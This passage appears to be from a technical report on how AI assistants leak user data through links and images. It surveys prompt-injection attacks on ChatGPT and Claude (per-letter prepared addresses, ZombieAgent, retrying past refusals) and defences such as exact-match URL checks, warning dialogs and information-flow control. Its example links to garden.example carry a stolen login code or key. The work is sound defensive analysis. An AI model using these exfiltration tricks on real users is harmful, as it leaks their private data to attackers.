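Rehberger reported ChatGPT's image leak to OpenAI in April 2023. The first countermeasure appeared that December, and Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* describes his initial tests of it. Before displaying an image, the ChatGPT website sent the image's address to an OpenAI service named `url_safe`, which classified it as safe or unsafe. OpenAI did not explain how the service decided. Rehberger tried 36 addresses on his own site, one for each letter and digit, and nine passed. He could see no reason why the image for "a" passed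 and the one for "d" did not. He leaked the word "hi" in two requests.

The ChatGPT website called `url_safe`, so other versions of ChatGPT needed their own code to call it, and the iPhone app had none. Willison (2023) described the solution as "half-baked" and expected attackers to get past it by hiding data in subdomains or file names.

The later gaps came from trusted domains. One was windows.net, where Microsoft rents online storage to the public. Rehberger opened a storage account there, made ChatGPT send a user's chat history to it inside an image address, and read the history in the account's logs. He had reported this gap and several others in October 2024. Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* says some still worked when he built the attack in 2025.

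The security company Tenable found another gap, which is more relevant to this design. By then, `url_safe` also checked clickable links, and ChatGPT left out any that failed. According to Tenable's *HackedGPT*, addresses on bing.com always passed. Bing gives every page in its search results a fixed bing.com address that forwards visitors to the page. Tenable couldn't add stolen data to these addresses, because they stop working if anyone changes them. Instead, its researchers got Bing to index one page for each letter of the alphabet. ChatGPT could then spell out a word by displaying the Bing addresses for its letters in order. This let data out even though every address was unaltered and existed before the conversation.

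According to Embrace The Red, a stronger version of the check appeared around August 2025 and stopped the attacks Rehberger had presented. The check uses an index that OpenAI built itself and explained in a technical paper in January 2026. Rehberger had guessed in 2023 that OpenAI might be looking addresses up in Bing's index.

### How much a choice can reveal

The model's choice between public addresses can reveal a secret even if the addresses themselves contain none. For example, an attacker with two public pages could use hidden instructions to tell the assistant to open one if the user plans to resign and the other if not. The attacker could then see which page received a visit and learn whether the user plans to resign.

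A choice between two equally likely possibilities conveys one bit. If the assistant may open any of N addresses, one visit can distinguish at most N possibilities:

information per choice ≤ log₂ N bits

A series of k choices among N addresses has Nᵏ possible sequences, and the attacker needs at least as many sequences as the secret has possible values. A six-digit code has a million possible values, or 19.93 bits. With 36 addresses, each choice conveys up to 5.17 bits, so the attacker needs at least four choices. Four allow 1,679,616 sequences, while three allow only 46,656.

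The last column of the table is for a random 20-character key made of lowercase letters and digits, which contains 103.4 bits.

| Permitted addresses | Bits per choice | Choices for a six-digit code | Choices for a 20-character key |
|---|---|---|---|
| 2 | 1.00 | 20 | 104 |
| 10 | 3.32 | 6 | 32 |
| 36 | 5.17 | 4 | 20 |
| 1,000 | 9.97 | 2 | 11 |
| 1,000,000 | 19.93 | 1 | 6 |

These numbers are minimums. To send the code in four choices, the model would have to convert it to base 36 and might make a mistake. Opening one page per digit is easier but takes six choices.

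Even so, Safe Url greatly reduces how much data each request can leak. A choice among 36 fixed addresses conveys about five bits, compared with roughly 10,000 bits for a 2,000-character address that the model can write freely.

The bottom row of the table shows a case where the protection would fail completely. If the index contained a million numbered pages from an attacker's site, one for every possible code, the model could write the address ending in the stolen code and the check would find an exact match. A crawler would probably not record a million nearly identical pages on an obscure site, but smaller numbers are easier to reach. Embrace The Red points out that anyone with a larger blog probably already has 36 pages in the index, and suggests that an attacker could extend the list to thousands. OpenAI's technical paper acknowledges the technique of using one address per letter.

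### Why clicks make repeated choices expensive

When software fetches the pages, an attacker can leak data through many small choices of which page to open instead of one large choice. An agent can open many pages without anyone having to approve each visit, and the 20 requests it takes to leak a key are not many for an agent doing research.

If a person has to click, the attacker needs a pretext for every link, and the user has to click them all. Suppose a user has a 50% chance of clicking each link. The chance of clicking all of them is about 6% for four links and about one in a million for 20. A user who skips one link or clicks two in the wrong order also garbles the message.

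A single click can still convey a small secret, such as the user's age group or which of 36 companies they are negotiating with. Hovering over the link would reveal nothing suspicious, because the address is an ordinary public one with no data in it. Exact matching therefore protects keys and emails well against theft through clicked links, but it offers little protection for small secrets like these. The application also has to check the links in its answers as well as the pages it fetches itself.

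### Attacks with prepared addresses

In 2024, ChatGPT followed a different rule and opened a web address only if it appeared in the user's prompt. Schwartzman (2024), in *Exfiltration of personal information from ChatGPT via prompt injection*, got around this rule by preparing the addresses in advance and burying them, along with the attacker's instructions, in a long piece of text such as computer code. The attack required the victim to paste this text into ChatGPT, which made the addresses part of the prompt.

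In Schwartzman's first demonstration, each address stood for an age group, and ChatGPT opened the one that fitted the user. It could choose the group from a remark about retiring in five years, without knowing the user's exact age. The second demonstration sent a postal code, using a separate address for each digit in the code. ChatGPT would also open a shortened form of any address in the prompt, so the length it opened could represent the digit's value. The model often chose the wrong length by itself, so Schwartzman had it run a short program to work out the right one.

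ChatGPT opened at most ten addresses per prompt, which limited the attack to ten characters at a time. Ten digits carry about 33 bits, enough for a postal code or a login code. Schwartzman reported the problem to OpenAI through its bug-reporting service, which marked the report as not applicable.

The security company Radware used the same principle the following year. Its earlier attack, ShadowLeak, had made Deep Research add personal data to an address and open it. Radware's *ShadowLeak* reports that the agent sometimes refused, so the attack's instructions told it to keep trying. OpenAI then introduced a stricter rule that let ChatGPT open addresses only as it had received them, with nothing added.

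Radware's *ZombieAgent* describes how the company got around that rule. The attacker sent the victim an email containing instructions and a list of complete addresses, each standing for one character. When the user asked ChatGPT to do something with Gmail, it read the email, found the private data and opened the matching addresses one by one. This complied with the rule because ChatGPT never changed an address. The requests came from OpenAI's servers before the user saw an answer. To keep the characters in order, Radware prepared a separate set of addresses for each position, so covering letters and digits in ten positions took 360 addresses instead of 36.

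Radware reported ZombieAgent on September 26, 2025, and three days later sent an improved version that it said worked every time. OpenAI fixed the vulnerability on December 16, and Radware published its account in January 2026. According to Ars Technica's *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, ChatGPT now opens a link from an email only if the address is in a well-known public index or the user has supplied it in the chat. An attacker who makes up 360 addresses must now get them into the index before ChatGPT can open them from an email.

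Without a public index, limits on which addresses an assistant can open may still let data leak, as happened with Anthropic's Claude. In September 2025, Anthropic released a web-fetching tool that did not let Claude construct addresses itself (Willison, 2025). In the chat product, Claude could open exact addresses that the user had typed or that its search tool had returned. Willison (2026) had been impressed by this design, but the researcher Ayush Paul found that Claude could also follow links on pages it had already fetched. Paul built a site with instructions for Claude to identify its user by browsing a directory letter by letter, where each page offered a new set of links. By following them, Claude spelled out the user's name, home city and employer.

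In *The Read-Only Lie*, a blog post drafted with an AI model, dyb counts 27 links on each page, or 4.75 bits per choice, and estimates that the whole attack took about 30 requests and conveyed some 143 bits. Anthropic said it had already found the problem internally, and it stopped Claude from following links in fetched pages. Paul's server could create new links for every visit, but under OpenAI's method he would have needed to publish them beforehand and wait for the crawler.

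One later test suggests that ChatGPT's defences work well together. *The Framing Gap* (August 2026) compared the ChatGPT product with an OpenAI model accessed directly through a programming interface. The model leaked a secret in up to 100% of trials, depending on the attack, while the product leaked nothing in 48 valid trials. The researchers couldn't see inside the product and did not attribute the result to Safe Url or any other safeguard. Zero leaks in 48 trials is also compatible with a true leak rate of up to about 6%.

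### Caching, repeat visits and missing checks

On Embrace The Red, Rehberger proposes two ways to make prepared addresses less useful. ChatGPT could cache each page, keeping a copy for a few minutes to reuse if the model requests the page again, or it could refuse to visit the same address twice in a session. Either way, the attacker's server would receive only one request per address, so if a model spelled out "hello", the server would not receive the second L. Rehberger presents these measures as extra obstacles, not complete solutions, and had not tested whether OpenAI already used them.

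The arithmetic supports his caution. With 36 addresses and no repeats, four visits still allow 36 × 35 × 34 × 33 = 1,413,720 sequences, more than enough for a six-digit code. An attacker can also prepare two addresses for the letter L, so that a word with two Ls needs no repeat. Scrambling the order of the requests would help slightly more than banning repeats, because an attacker who could see which pages were visited, but not in what order, would need six visits for the code instead of four.

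In 2023 Rehberger suggested a limit on the number of images in an answer, which restricts the channel more directly. But the limit has to be very low to protect a short code. Three visits to pages chosen from a set of 36 would narrow a million possible codes to about 21, and a login page that allowed several attempts might let the attacker guess the right one.

OpenAI took caching much further in Lockdown Mode, an optional setting for people who handle sensitive data. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) explains that in this mode ChatGPT reads web pages only from stored copies, and browsing sends no live requests outside OpenAI's network. A page's owner can't tell that ChatGPT has read it, so the choice of pages reveals nothing to them, however many pages there are. OpenAI released the setting to business customers in February 2026 and to personal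 accounts in June.

The restrictions considerably reduce what ChatGPT can do. OpenAI's help page *Lockdown Mode* warns that search results may be out of date or missing, and that Deep Research and agent mode don't work at all. The setting doesn't affect network access in Codex, OpenAI's coding assistant. The page's list of restrictions doesn't mention ordinary links in answers. If ChatGPT still shows them, clicking one would send a live request from the user's own browser.

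Rehberger's remaining concern is that a developer at OpenAI may build a new feature without knowing that the check exists. He writes that he often met this problem in his own security work. This had happened before, when the iPhone and Mac apps lacked `url_safe`. PromptArmor found a similar omission in the pages where developers review the logs of applications built on OpenAI's models. Those pages displayed Markdown images insecurely, so a developer who had blocked images in the application could still leak a user's data by opening a suspicious answer in the log.

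Lockdown Mode had a similar gap. The Hacker News' *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction* (2026) reported in November that a flaw in ChatGPT's preview of HTML pages let chat data out despite the restrictions. OpenAI has since patched the flaw.

### Harmless addresses that fail the test

Many useful addresses are not in any public index. A news article published minutes ago may not have been indexed yet. A link to a shared document, a parcel tracking page or a boarding pass may be meant for one person. Websites also generate addresses on request, such as those for search results or map directions, and newsletters add tracking codes to otherwise public links. An assistant that reads email will come across all of these.

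The check can't distinguish an address containing a parcel number from one containing a stolen login code, because the crawler has encountered neither. Exact matching avoids the false alarms that a strict domain list raises for public pages on little-known sites, but it adds one for every new or personal address on a well-known site. OpenAI doesn't report in either post how often these false alarms occur.

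An application could reduce the number by removing known tracking codes from an address and checking whether the rest is known to be public. It would then have to open the address without those codes instead of the original.

Another way is to trust addresses that the user supplies. According to Embrace The Red, ChatGPT appears to treat an address in a user's message as safe for the rest of the session. This is reasonable when someone types an address or copies it from a browser. It is riskier when they paste a long text written by someone else, which is how Schwartzman got his addresses into the prompt.

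### Private data in addresses that are already public

Safe Url also assumes that public addresses rarely contain private data. In *The Silent Spill*, Ramadan, Mannan and colleagues (2026) give some idea of how often such addresses do. Between January and April 2025, they collected 6,094,475 addresses from web archives, text-sharing sites and services that scan links for malware. Some companies' email security systems automatically send suspicious links to these scanners, which often publish the addresses they receive, so a private link can become public without its owner knowing.

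The researchers' software searched the addresses and the pages behind them for signs of exposed data, and flagged 12,331 addresses, or 0.2%. These included 26 working password-reset links, 83 API keys and 12 contracts or similar documents awaiting signature that strangers could open. The researchers checked 12 to 34 cases by hand in each of eight categories and found that up to 15% were false alarms. When they revisited 2,000 of the flagged addresses after 75 days, 38% were still open to anyone.

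The 0.2% may be too high or too low for OpenAI's index. Ramadan and colleagues deliberately searched sites that handle payments, logins and documents, and a crawler that follows links between public pages would probably find fewer private addresses. But their software discarded every address that no longer worked, even though such an address can still contain a name or an email address.

The study shows that a public address can contain private data. But if a password-reset link, for example, is already in a public archive, an attacker can read it there and gains little when ChatGPT opens it. Safe Url protects secrets that exist only in the user's conversation or mailbox, and those are not in the index.

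Opening a private address automatically could cause a different problem if the visit triggered an action, such as confirming an order. The researchers used their own accounts to test the 24 kinds of password-reset and backup-code links in their collection, and found that a visit alone changed nothing. They did not test other kinds of links.

The scanners could also publish a link that an assistant had written, if the user forwarded the answer and the recipient's email security system submitted the link. A crawler that read the scanner's reports could then add the address, including the stolen code, to its index. This is an inference, and the study did not observe it. Ramadan and colleagues recommend that scanners hide values that look like keys or tokens before publishing an address, but say automatic masking may miss secrets in unusual encodings.

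## Checks and warnings when the user clicks

An application can still stop a request after the user clicks a link, because the app or web page receives the click before the browser opens the address. It can then check the address, show a warning or refuse to open it. ChatGPT shows a warning for some links and lets the user decide, while Microsoft 365 Copilot looks up whether the destination is dangerous.

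### ChatGPT's warning about unverified links

When ChatGPT can't match a link's exact address to OpenAI's index of public pages, it may open a dialog titled "Check this link is safe". In a picture OpenAI published in January 2026, the dialog shows the address and a warning that ChatGPT hasn't verified the link and that opening it may share data from the conversation with another site. The user can then copy the link or open it. A user who copies the link can inspect it in a text editor, but can also paste it straight into a browser. OpenAI advises users who think something looks wrong to avoid the link and ask ChatGPT for another source or a summary.

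OpenAI's help page *ChatGPT generated links* gives an example of a harmless link that sends personal data. A user who lives in London asks where to buy a car, and ChatGPT offers a link to a car-search site with "London" in the address. Clicking the link tells the site where the user lives, which also makes the link useful. An attacker's link can send a login code in the same way. OpenAI asks the user because only they know which of these they would agree to send.

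The help page describes the dialog as a request to approve the information in the link, but its advice to users is to check which website the link leads to and make sure they trust it. This advice would have helped the developer in the Slack AI demonstration, who had no reason to visit an unfamiliar domain. It helps less after a web search, when most of the sites in the answer may be new to the user.

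When a website's owner asks OpenAI not to index its pages, ChatGPT shows a confirmation warning for every link to that site. People who often read such a site will see the warning even for ordinary public articles, so how often it appears depends partly on factors unrelated to risk.

### Safe Links in Copilot

According to Microsoft, Safe Links is a service for businesses that scans and rewrites links in incoming email and checks them again when somebody clicks. Gandhi (2025), in *SafeLinks Protection for Links Generated by M365 Copilot Chat and Office Apps*, announced that this check on clicking now also covered links in Copilot Chat's answers, on computers and phones. It requires a Microsoft Defender for Office 365 licence. For customers without one, Copilot Chat has a built-in check of the address's reputation. Windows Report's *Microsoft 365 Copilot Chat gets SafeLinks for better user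 safety* explains that a risky link brings up a warning and a link that passes opens as usual.

Checking a link when the user clicks it, rather than when the answer appears, can catch a site that somebody reported in between, since the user may click a day later. Safe Links also gives a company's security staff a record of clicks on malicious links in Copilot Chat.

But a reputation check, like Gemini's address filter, tests whether the destination is known to be bad, so an attacker's new domain could pass. Gandhi's announcement doesn't mention any check for private data in the address.

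Microsoft also announced that Copilot Chat no longer hides a link if it appears in the grounding data, the material Copilot used to write the answer. Gandhi doesn't explain how closely the address must match. If the whole address has to match, this is a reasonable defence against data theft, because an attacker can't write an address in advance that contains a login code they don't know. However, the grounding data may include the attacker's own email. The attacker could list many complete addresses there, as Radware did in its attack on ChatGPT, and tell the model to show the one that fits the user's data.

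### What a useful warning would show

To decide well, the user needs to know where the link leads, what data it will send and why it is in the answer. A dialog that prints the address shows where the link leads, at least to people who can pick out the host name. Whether it also reveals the data depends on how the attacker has told the model to write it. The table shows what a user might see if a link to the invented site garden.example contained the login code 482913.

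| How the model writes the code | What the dialog prints after `garden.example/guides` |
|---|---|
| Plain digits | `?c=482913` |
| Percent-encoding | `?c=%34%38%32%39%31%33` |
| Base64 | `?c=NDgyOTEz` |
| Tag characters, displayed as Unicode | `?c=` |
| Tag characters, percent-encoded | `?c=` and 72 more characters, starting `%F3%A0%80%B4` |

Only the first version is readable, and even then the user has to connect six digits with an email they may never have opened. The base64 version could be mistaken for a tracking code, and the fourth version appears to contain no data.

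Software can decode these addresses better than a person can. It can split the address at its slashes, question marks and ampersands, undo the percent-encoding, and convert any tag characters to the letters and digits they correspond to. It can then try decoding each piece as base64 and hexadecimal, and search the assistant's context for the results. Many harmless strings decode to nonsense, so the dialog should show a decoded piece only if it matches something in the context.

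The same search can help explain why the link is there. An attacker normally has to supply the host name, so it will usually appear in the attacker's message. The dialog could then read: "This link would send 482913 to garden.example. The number is in an email from your bank. The site's name is in an email from someone you have never written to." A user can understand that without knowing anything about web addresses. The user may click much later, so the application would have to run the search when it writes the answer and store the result with the link.

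An attacker could get around the search by choosing an unusual encoding. In Greshake and colleagues' demonstration, Bing Chat nearly spelled "John Smith" backwards, and instructions could also tell a model to replace each digit with the name of a flower. The search could also miss a summary of an email, which may share no long phrase with the original. So the dialog shouldn't suggest that a link is safe when the search finds nothing.

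OpenAI comes closest to offering such a dialog. It wrote in March 2026 that when its software detects that ChatGPT is about to send information from the conversation to a third party, the software either blocks the request or shows the user the information and asks for confirmation. But the dialog pictured in OpenAI's January post shows a web address, and neither post mentions decoding the address or telling the user where the data came from.

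### How people respond to browser warnings

No published study seems to measure how often people click links in an assistant's answer that contain their own data, or how often a warning stops them. The nearest evidence comes from studies of browser warnings, phishing emails and AI agents that ask for permission.

Akhawe and Felt (2013), in *Alice in Warningland*, measured what people did when Chrome or Firefox warned them about a site. They used data the browsers collected from consenting users during normal browsing in May and June 2013, covering just over 25 million warnings. Earlier laboratory studies had suggested that most people ignore such warnings, but in one of them more than 40% of participants said the laboratory setting had influenced them to continue.

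In the field, people continued past 9% to 23% of warnings about malware and phishing. For SSL warnings, which appear when the browser can't confirm a site's identity, the rate was 33% in Firefox and 70.2% in Chrome.

Part of that gap exists because Firefox saved a user's decision to trust a site, while Chrome repeated the warning at every visit. Akhawe and Felt give the example of a user who turns back from one site and visits another nine times. The user's click-through rate would be 50% in Firefox and 90% in Chrome for the same behaviour. Chrome also gave users no way past the warning on some important sites, which could account for up to 15 points of the difference.

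Repetition may also matter. Of the Chrome users who continued, 47% decided within 1.5 seconds, while the same share of those who left took 3.5 seconds. People also clicked fastest through the most common type of error, which Akhawe and Felt interpret as a sign of warning fatigue. Users clicked "Help me understand" on only 1.6% of Chrome's SSL warnings, and nobody opened Firefox's technical details. If a link dialog put the decoded data behind a "Details" button, probably few users would open it.

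The malware and phishing warnings were almost always right, but SSL warnings often came from harmless sites that were badly configured. ChatGPT's warning is more like the SSL warning, because many harmless links also trigger it. If one unverified link in 10,000 contains stolen data and a user sees five warnings a week, the user would encounter a real attack once every 38 years on average. The user could easily get into the habit of clicking "open" without reading the warning.

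*Tuning out security warnings* (Vance, Jenkins and colleagues, 2018) tracked how that habit formed in a field experiment with permission warnings. People obeyed the warnings much less often by the end of three weeks, but the decline was much slower among those whose warnings kept changing in appearance. *Paying Attention to Notifications* (BYU Marriott School of Business, 2018) reports a 20% benefit from small visual changes.

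A warning's design can also change what people do without changing what they understand. eWeek's *Google Study Shows Users Fail to Understand Security Warnings* describes research by Google and the University of Pennsylvania in which graphics that promoted the safest choice led many more people to take it, although few understood the threat or which data was at risk. That is a good result for a malware warning, but when a link may lead to a shared document or a parcel page, steering everyone away would also keep users from many links they want.

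### What phishing experiments show about clicks

Experiments with simulated phishing emails are useful evidence here because they usually measure clicks, and data theft through a link requires only a click.

Ho, Mirian and colleagues (2025), in *Understanding the Efficacy of Phishing Training in Practice*, analysed an eight-month trial at UC San Diego Health, a large medical centre. The 19,789 employees in the trial were randomly assigned to five groups and received simulated phishing emails about once a month. Employees in the control group who clicked saw an ordinary error page. Those in the other four groups who clicked saw training material, which was either general or about that email, and was presented as either a fixed page or an interactive exercise.

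On average, the trained groups clicked 1.7 percentage points less often than the control group. One reason the difference was so small is that people hardly used the material. More than half of the training sessions ended within 10 seconds, and people completed fewer than a quarter. Those who finished an interactive exercise were 19% less likely to click on a later email, but they may have been more careful to begin with. Ho and colleagues also found no link between how recently someone had taken the yearly security course and how likely they were to click.

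The wording of the email affected click rates far more than the training did. About 1.8% of recipients clicked on a message about their Outlook password, compared with 30.8% for one about a change in vacation policy. In the first month 9.7% of employees clicked, and by the eighth month 56% had clicked at least once. An attacker who can try several pretexts therefore has a good chance of getting a click from any particular person. These emails were unsolicited, whereas a link in an assistant's answer follows the user's own question. That may make people more willing to click, though the trial can't show by how much.

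In *URL Inspection Tasks*, Lain, Nakatsuka and colleagues (2025) tested the effect of software that intervenes after a user clicks a link. They recruited 2,673 people in the United States, Germany and Japan to play employees of an invented company and work through an inbox of legitimate and phishing emails. Some participants went straight to the site when they clicked a link, while others first had to complete one of several tasks involving its address.

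| After clicking, the participant | Phishing emails that succeeded (%) |
|---|---|
| Went straight to the site | 74 |
| Dragged parts of the address back into place | 61 |
| Saw the address again and confirmed | 57 |
| Had to identify the site's domain | 35 |

The third row is the most similar to ChatGPT's dialog. Showing the address again helped, but more than half of the phishing emails still succeeded. The last row combines three tasks, in which people picked the domain from a list, highlighted it or typed it. If their answer didn't match the real domain, the software warned them. The tasks worked best against misspelled domains, where phishing success fell from 79% to 17%. They took 7 to 10 seconds on average and annoyed people somewhat, so Lain and colleagues recommend using them only occasionally, mainly in places that need high security.

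These tasks work by showing users that a link doesn't lead where they meant to go. Someone who clicks a source in an assistant's answer may have no particular site in mind, and would correctly identify garden.example without noticing the login code after it in the URL. A version for assistants would have to direct the user's attention to the data there.

### How often people approve an AI agent's requests

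Programmers who use AI agents often have to approve the agents' actions one at a time. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, used to ask for permission by default before running a command or changing a file. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* says this led to "approval fatigue", in which people gradually stop paying attention to what they approve. Resilient Cyber's *The Human in the Loop Illusion* cites Anthropic's figure that users approved 93% of these requests, and argues that human review was therefore not a meaningful safeguard.

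A high approval rate can't show that by itself, because most commands are harmless and users should approve them. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) puts the rate at 97% and describes a controlled test in which a research company had 1,053 paid testers work with the agent on coding tasks. The testers knew they were being evaluated, but not for what. Once per session, the software replaced the text of a permission request with a clearly dangerous command that would never run.

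The testers refused the command in 143 cases, or 13.6%. They refused about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more requests. Anthropic's automated check, which uses a model to review each action, blocked 937 of the same commands, or 89.0%. The testers refused only six of the commands that the check allowed. If they had reviewed everything the check allowed and made the same decisions, the share of dangerous commands stopped would have risen to 89.6%.

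Anthropic ran this comparison while preparing to replace the permission requests with the automated check. The testers might have been more careful if they had been protecting their own files. But the artificial setting alone doesn't easily explain the decline over a session, since the setting stayed the same throughout.

People were also far less passive about other questions, and rejected 39% of the plans that Claude presented for approval. Many of those rejections were probably about taste or approach, not safety, but they show that people read requests about things they understand and care about. "Send this login code to garden.example?" is closer to that kind of request than a percent-encoded URL is.

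Li, Dai and colleagues (2026), in *Are You Sure?*, studied people using an assistant that an attacker had already compromised. The 303 participants each completed three of nine tasks, such as choosing a job candidate or answering email. One group saw a single notice about risks at the start, another saw a small reminder beside every answer, and a third got an alert that interrupted them when the assistant's output was suspicious. Afterwards, 8.6% of the notice group, 20% of the reminder group and 25% of the alert group reported noticing anything unusual. The paper gives two sets of group sizes. If the reminder and alert groups had 60 people each, as one of its tables indicates, only three more people reported noticing something in the alert group than in the reminder group.

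The alert's effect varied widely between tasks. In the web search task, the share of people who noticed something rose from 9.8% with the opening notice to 50% with the alert, but in the email task it rose only from 9.3% to 15%. Li and colleagues think the difference comes from how much effort it takes to check the assistant's work. This supports decoding the address for users so they don't have to do it themselves.

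Some participants who missed the attack trusted the assistant more after seeing the warnings, which they took as a sign of a well-protected system. A link dialog might similarly make people less careful with links that bring up no warning. These would include prepared public addresses, which can leak data one choice at a time.

None of the nine tasks measured clicks on a link. *I know it's not right, but that's what it said to do* (2025) uses a design that researchers could adapt to measure them. Participants do real tasks with a working chatbot, without knowing that the study is about trust. The chatbot gives good advice in the first three tasks and bad advice in the last two. A study of links could add an address containing invented private data in the last two tasks, and compare a dialog that prints the address with one that decodes it.

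### Asking less often

OpenAI presents confirmation as a way to keep the user in control, and there is a good argument for that. The user may want to tell the car-search site about London, and blocking every unverified link would also block shared documents and boarding passes. The browser study also shows that people often heed warnings that are usually right.

The argument against these checks is that they give users little real control if users approve almost everything. Frequent requests can also lead people to turn off the protection. Anthropic found that 62% of Claude Code users had either turned off permission checks or told the software not to ask again about shell commands, the text commands that control a computer. OpenAI accepts part of this argument, which was one of its reasons for rejecting strict domain lists.

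OpenAI warns only about addresses it can't verify, but these still include many harmless ones. An application could narrow the warning to addresses in which it finds text from the user's emails or files. The London link would then open without a dialog if the user had mentioned the city only in the chat, but a link containing a login code from the mailbox would trigger a warning. The application would miss some attacks that encode the data in an unusual way, but users would give the remaining warnings more attention.

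In the clearest cases, the application can refuse without asking the user. Anthropic's automated check never approves an action that it classifies as sending code or secrets to an outside destination. A user who wants to do that has to leave the automatic mode or run the command personally. An assistant could similarly refuse to open an address that contains a password or login code from the user's mailbox, and offer the site's public page instead. A mistaken refusal would delay the user slightly, but a hurried user couldn't override a correct refusal with a single click.

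## Tracking where the contents of a link came from

Software that searches a link for text from the user's mailbox will miss text that the model has encoded in an unexpected way. Information-flow control tracks where data came from instead of what it looks like. It labels each piece of data on arrival and copies those labels to anything derived from it, so a login code keeps its labels even if the model replaces each digit with the name of a flower. Lan and colleagues suggest information-flow control for AI agents because the origin of a request can reveal an attack even when the request contains only four harmless-looking characters.

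### Labels for readers and for trust

Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, use two kinds of label. A confidentiality label lists the people who may read the data. If Ana, Ben and Carla may read one document, and Ben, Carla and Dev may read another, then only the people on both lists may read a summary of the two:

{Ana, Ben, Carla} ∩ {Ben, Carla, Dev} = {Ben, Carla}

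An integrity label marks data as trusted or untrusted. Anything derived from both trusted and untrusted data is untrusted. This label is independent of the one that marks data as private, so a stranger's email can be both private and untrusted.

The software also needs a way to assign the first labels. Costa and colleagues infer an email's permitted readers from its sender and recipients, though they note that somebody may have shared it more widely. Trust is harder to infer, because a mail server can often confirm which domain sent an email but not that its contents are safe.

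### A rule for links

The text of an answer goes only to the user, but a clicked link's address also goes to the owner of the destination server. A system could therefore block or question a link when both of these conditions hold:

- Private data affected the address, and the destination's owner is not permitted to read that data.
- Untrusted content chose the destination or the form of the address, meaning which data goes into it and how.

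Suppose a user keeps the key to a weather service, `plum-5521`, in a private note. An outsider's email supplies the beginning of an address and tells the assistant to add the key. When the user asks for the key, the answer contains this link:

`https://garden.example/guides?c=plum-5521`

| Part of the address | Where it came from | Permitted readers | Trusted? |
|---|---|---|---|
| `https://garden.example/guides?c=` | The outsider's email | User and outsider | No |
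| `plum-5521` | The user's private note | User | Yes |
| The whole address | Both | User | No |

The owner of garden.example may not read the key, and an untrusted email chose the destination, so the system stops the link.

Either condition alone would stop too many links. If the user asks to see their home on a map, the assistant might offer `https://maps.example/search?q=14+Elm+Road`. The first condition alone would stop this link because the map company isn't a permitted reader of the home address. When both conditions are required, the link passes because the user asked for the map and the developer chose the site. The second condition alone would stop every link that the assistant copied from an unfamiliar web page, including links with nothing private in them.

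Lists of permitted readers also let software approve some links that an exact-match check can't verify. If a courier emails the user a parcel number, the courier is already a permitted reader of that number. The software can allow a link that sends the number back to the courier's site, provided it can match the sender's domain to the link's host.

The rule can still raise a false alarm. Suppose the user asks for directions from home to a plumber whose address is in an email:

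`https://maps.example/route?from=14+Elm+Road&to=3+Mill+Lane`

The plumber's email supplied only the destination in the map link. Because the model read the email before writing the link, the software can't determine whether the email also influenced the choice of map site. A cautious system therefore labels the whole URL untrusted and flags the link even though it is harmless.

Any token in a model's context may slightly affect any later token. *GIF* (2026) argues that a system that tries to rule out every such influence becomes either too cautious or too expensive to run. It proposes measuring how much the output reveals about a piece of the input, and intervening only when that amount exceeds a threshold. That would let many map links through, but it might also miss a one-bit secret, such as whether the user plans to resign.

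For common kinds of link, the application can avoid guessing where the contents came from by building the URL itself. For a map link, the model would supply only the start and end of the route, and ordinary code would put them into a fixed maps.example URL. The plumber's email could still give a false destination, but it couldn't send the user's home address to another server.

### Whether a click authorizes the release

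A map link has to release some private data to be useful. Security researchers call such a deliberate release declassification, and the danger is that an attacker may gain control of it. Zdancewic and Myers introduced a test for this, robust declassification. Myers, Sabelfeld and Zdancewic explain in *Enforcing Robust Declassification and Qualified Robustness* that an attacker should not be able to affect what information a system releases or whether it releases any. An attacker who interferes with a robust system learns no more than one who only watches it.

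A simple example is a program that publishes a secret if a switch is on. An attacker who can flip the switch controls whether the program releases the secret, and one who can replace the secret before the program publishes it controls what the program releases. The program is robust only if the attacker can do neither.

They also describe an attack on a password checker. Every password checker releases a little information, because it shows whether a guess was right. An attacker who could store some other secret in place of the password could use the checker to test guesses about that secret. The checker would be working as designed but releasing information that nobody meant it to.

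A click on an attacker's link has the same problem. In the Slack AI attack, the attacker's message determined what the click would release, and its false error notice influenced whether the developer clicked. Without that message, the developer's question would not have produced the link.

The developer agreed to open a page by clicking the link, but did not agree to send the key, because they had no reason to think that the click would send it. A user who asks for a map of their home and clicks the link comes much closer to agreeing to send their address, because they know that a map site needs it.

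A good counterargument is that a user who clearly sees the data and the recipient can authorize the release, even if an outsider proposed it. For example, a landlord might email a tenant a link to a form that asks for a phone number. The landlord chose the destination and the data, but the tenant can still decide to send the number. OpenAI's confirmation dialog is based on the same idea.

Myers and colleagues also accept that strict robustness rules out some reasonable systems. In one of their examples, a company offers two pieces of confidential information for sale and lets an untrusted customer choose which one to buy. The customer affects what the company releases, but the company is willing to release either piece. To allow such cases, they add endorsement, an explicit step that treats an untrusted value as trusted. They call the weaker guarantee qualified robustness. Untrusted code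 may not endorse its own values.

A dialog that shows the data and the recipient could serve as the endorsement step for a link. Ordinary software would have to write the dialog, because an attacker's instructions could shape one written by the model. The approval should cover only the value and destination shown. Even then, the attacker can influence the user's decision with a good pretext, so the dialog doesn't meet the strict test. A user who reads the dialog can give real consent by clicking, but the studies of browser warnings and permission requests suggest many users won't read it.

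Asking once for a broad permission would reduce the number of dialogs, but Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, give a reason not to do this for private data. Their agent, Prudentia, lets a user endorse an email so that the agent can act on everything in it. The user can then approve an email listing ten tasks once instead of approving ten actions. They decided against an equivalent permission to release private data because whether a release is appropriate depends heavily on the situation. For example, a user who sends their home address to a map site hasn't agreed to send it to garden.example.

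### How CaMeL and FIDES treat the answer

Two systems from 2025, CaMeL from Google DeepMind and FIDES from Microsoft, apply information-flow control to AI agents. Both use ordinary code to check labels before the agent calls a tool.

*CaMeLoT* (2026), which extends CaMeL, explains how the original divides work between two models. The privileged model receives the user's request and writes a plan as a short program in a restricted form of Python. The quarantined model reads untrusted content but can't issue instructions to the privileged model, so a stranger's email can't add a step to the plan that sends the user's key away. An interpreter runs the program and records where each value came from and who may read it. Before each tool call, the interpreter checks these records against a policy.

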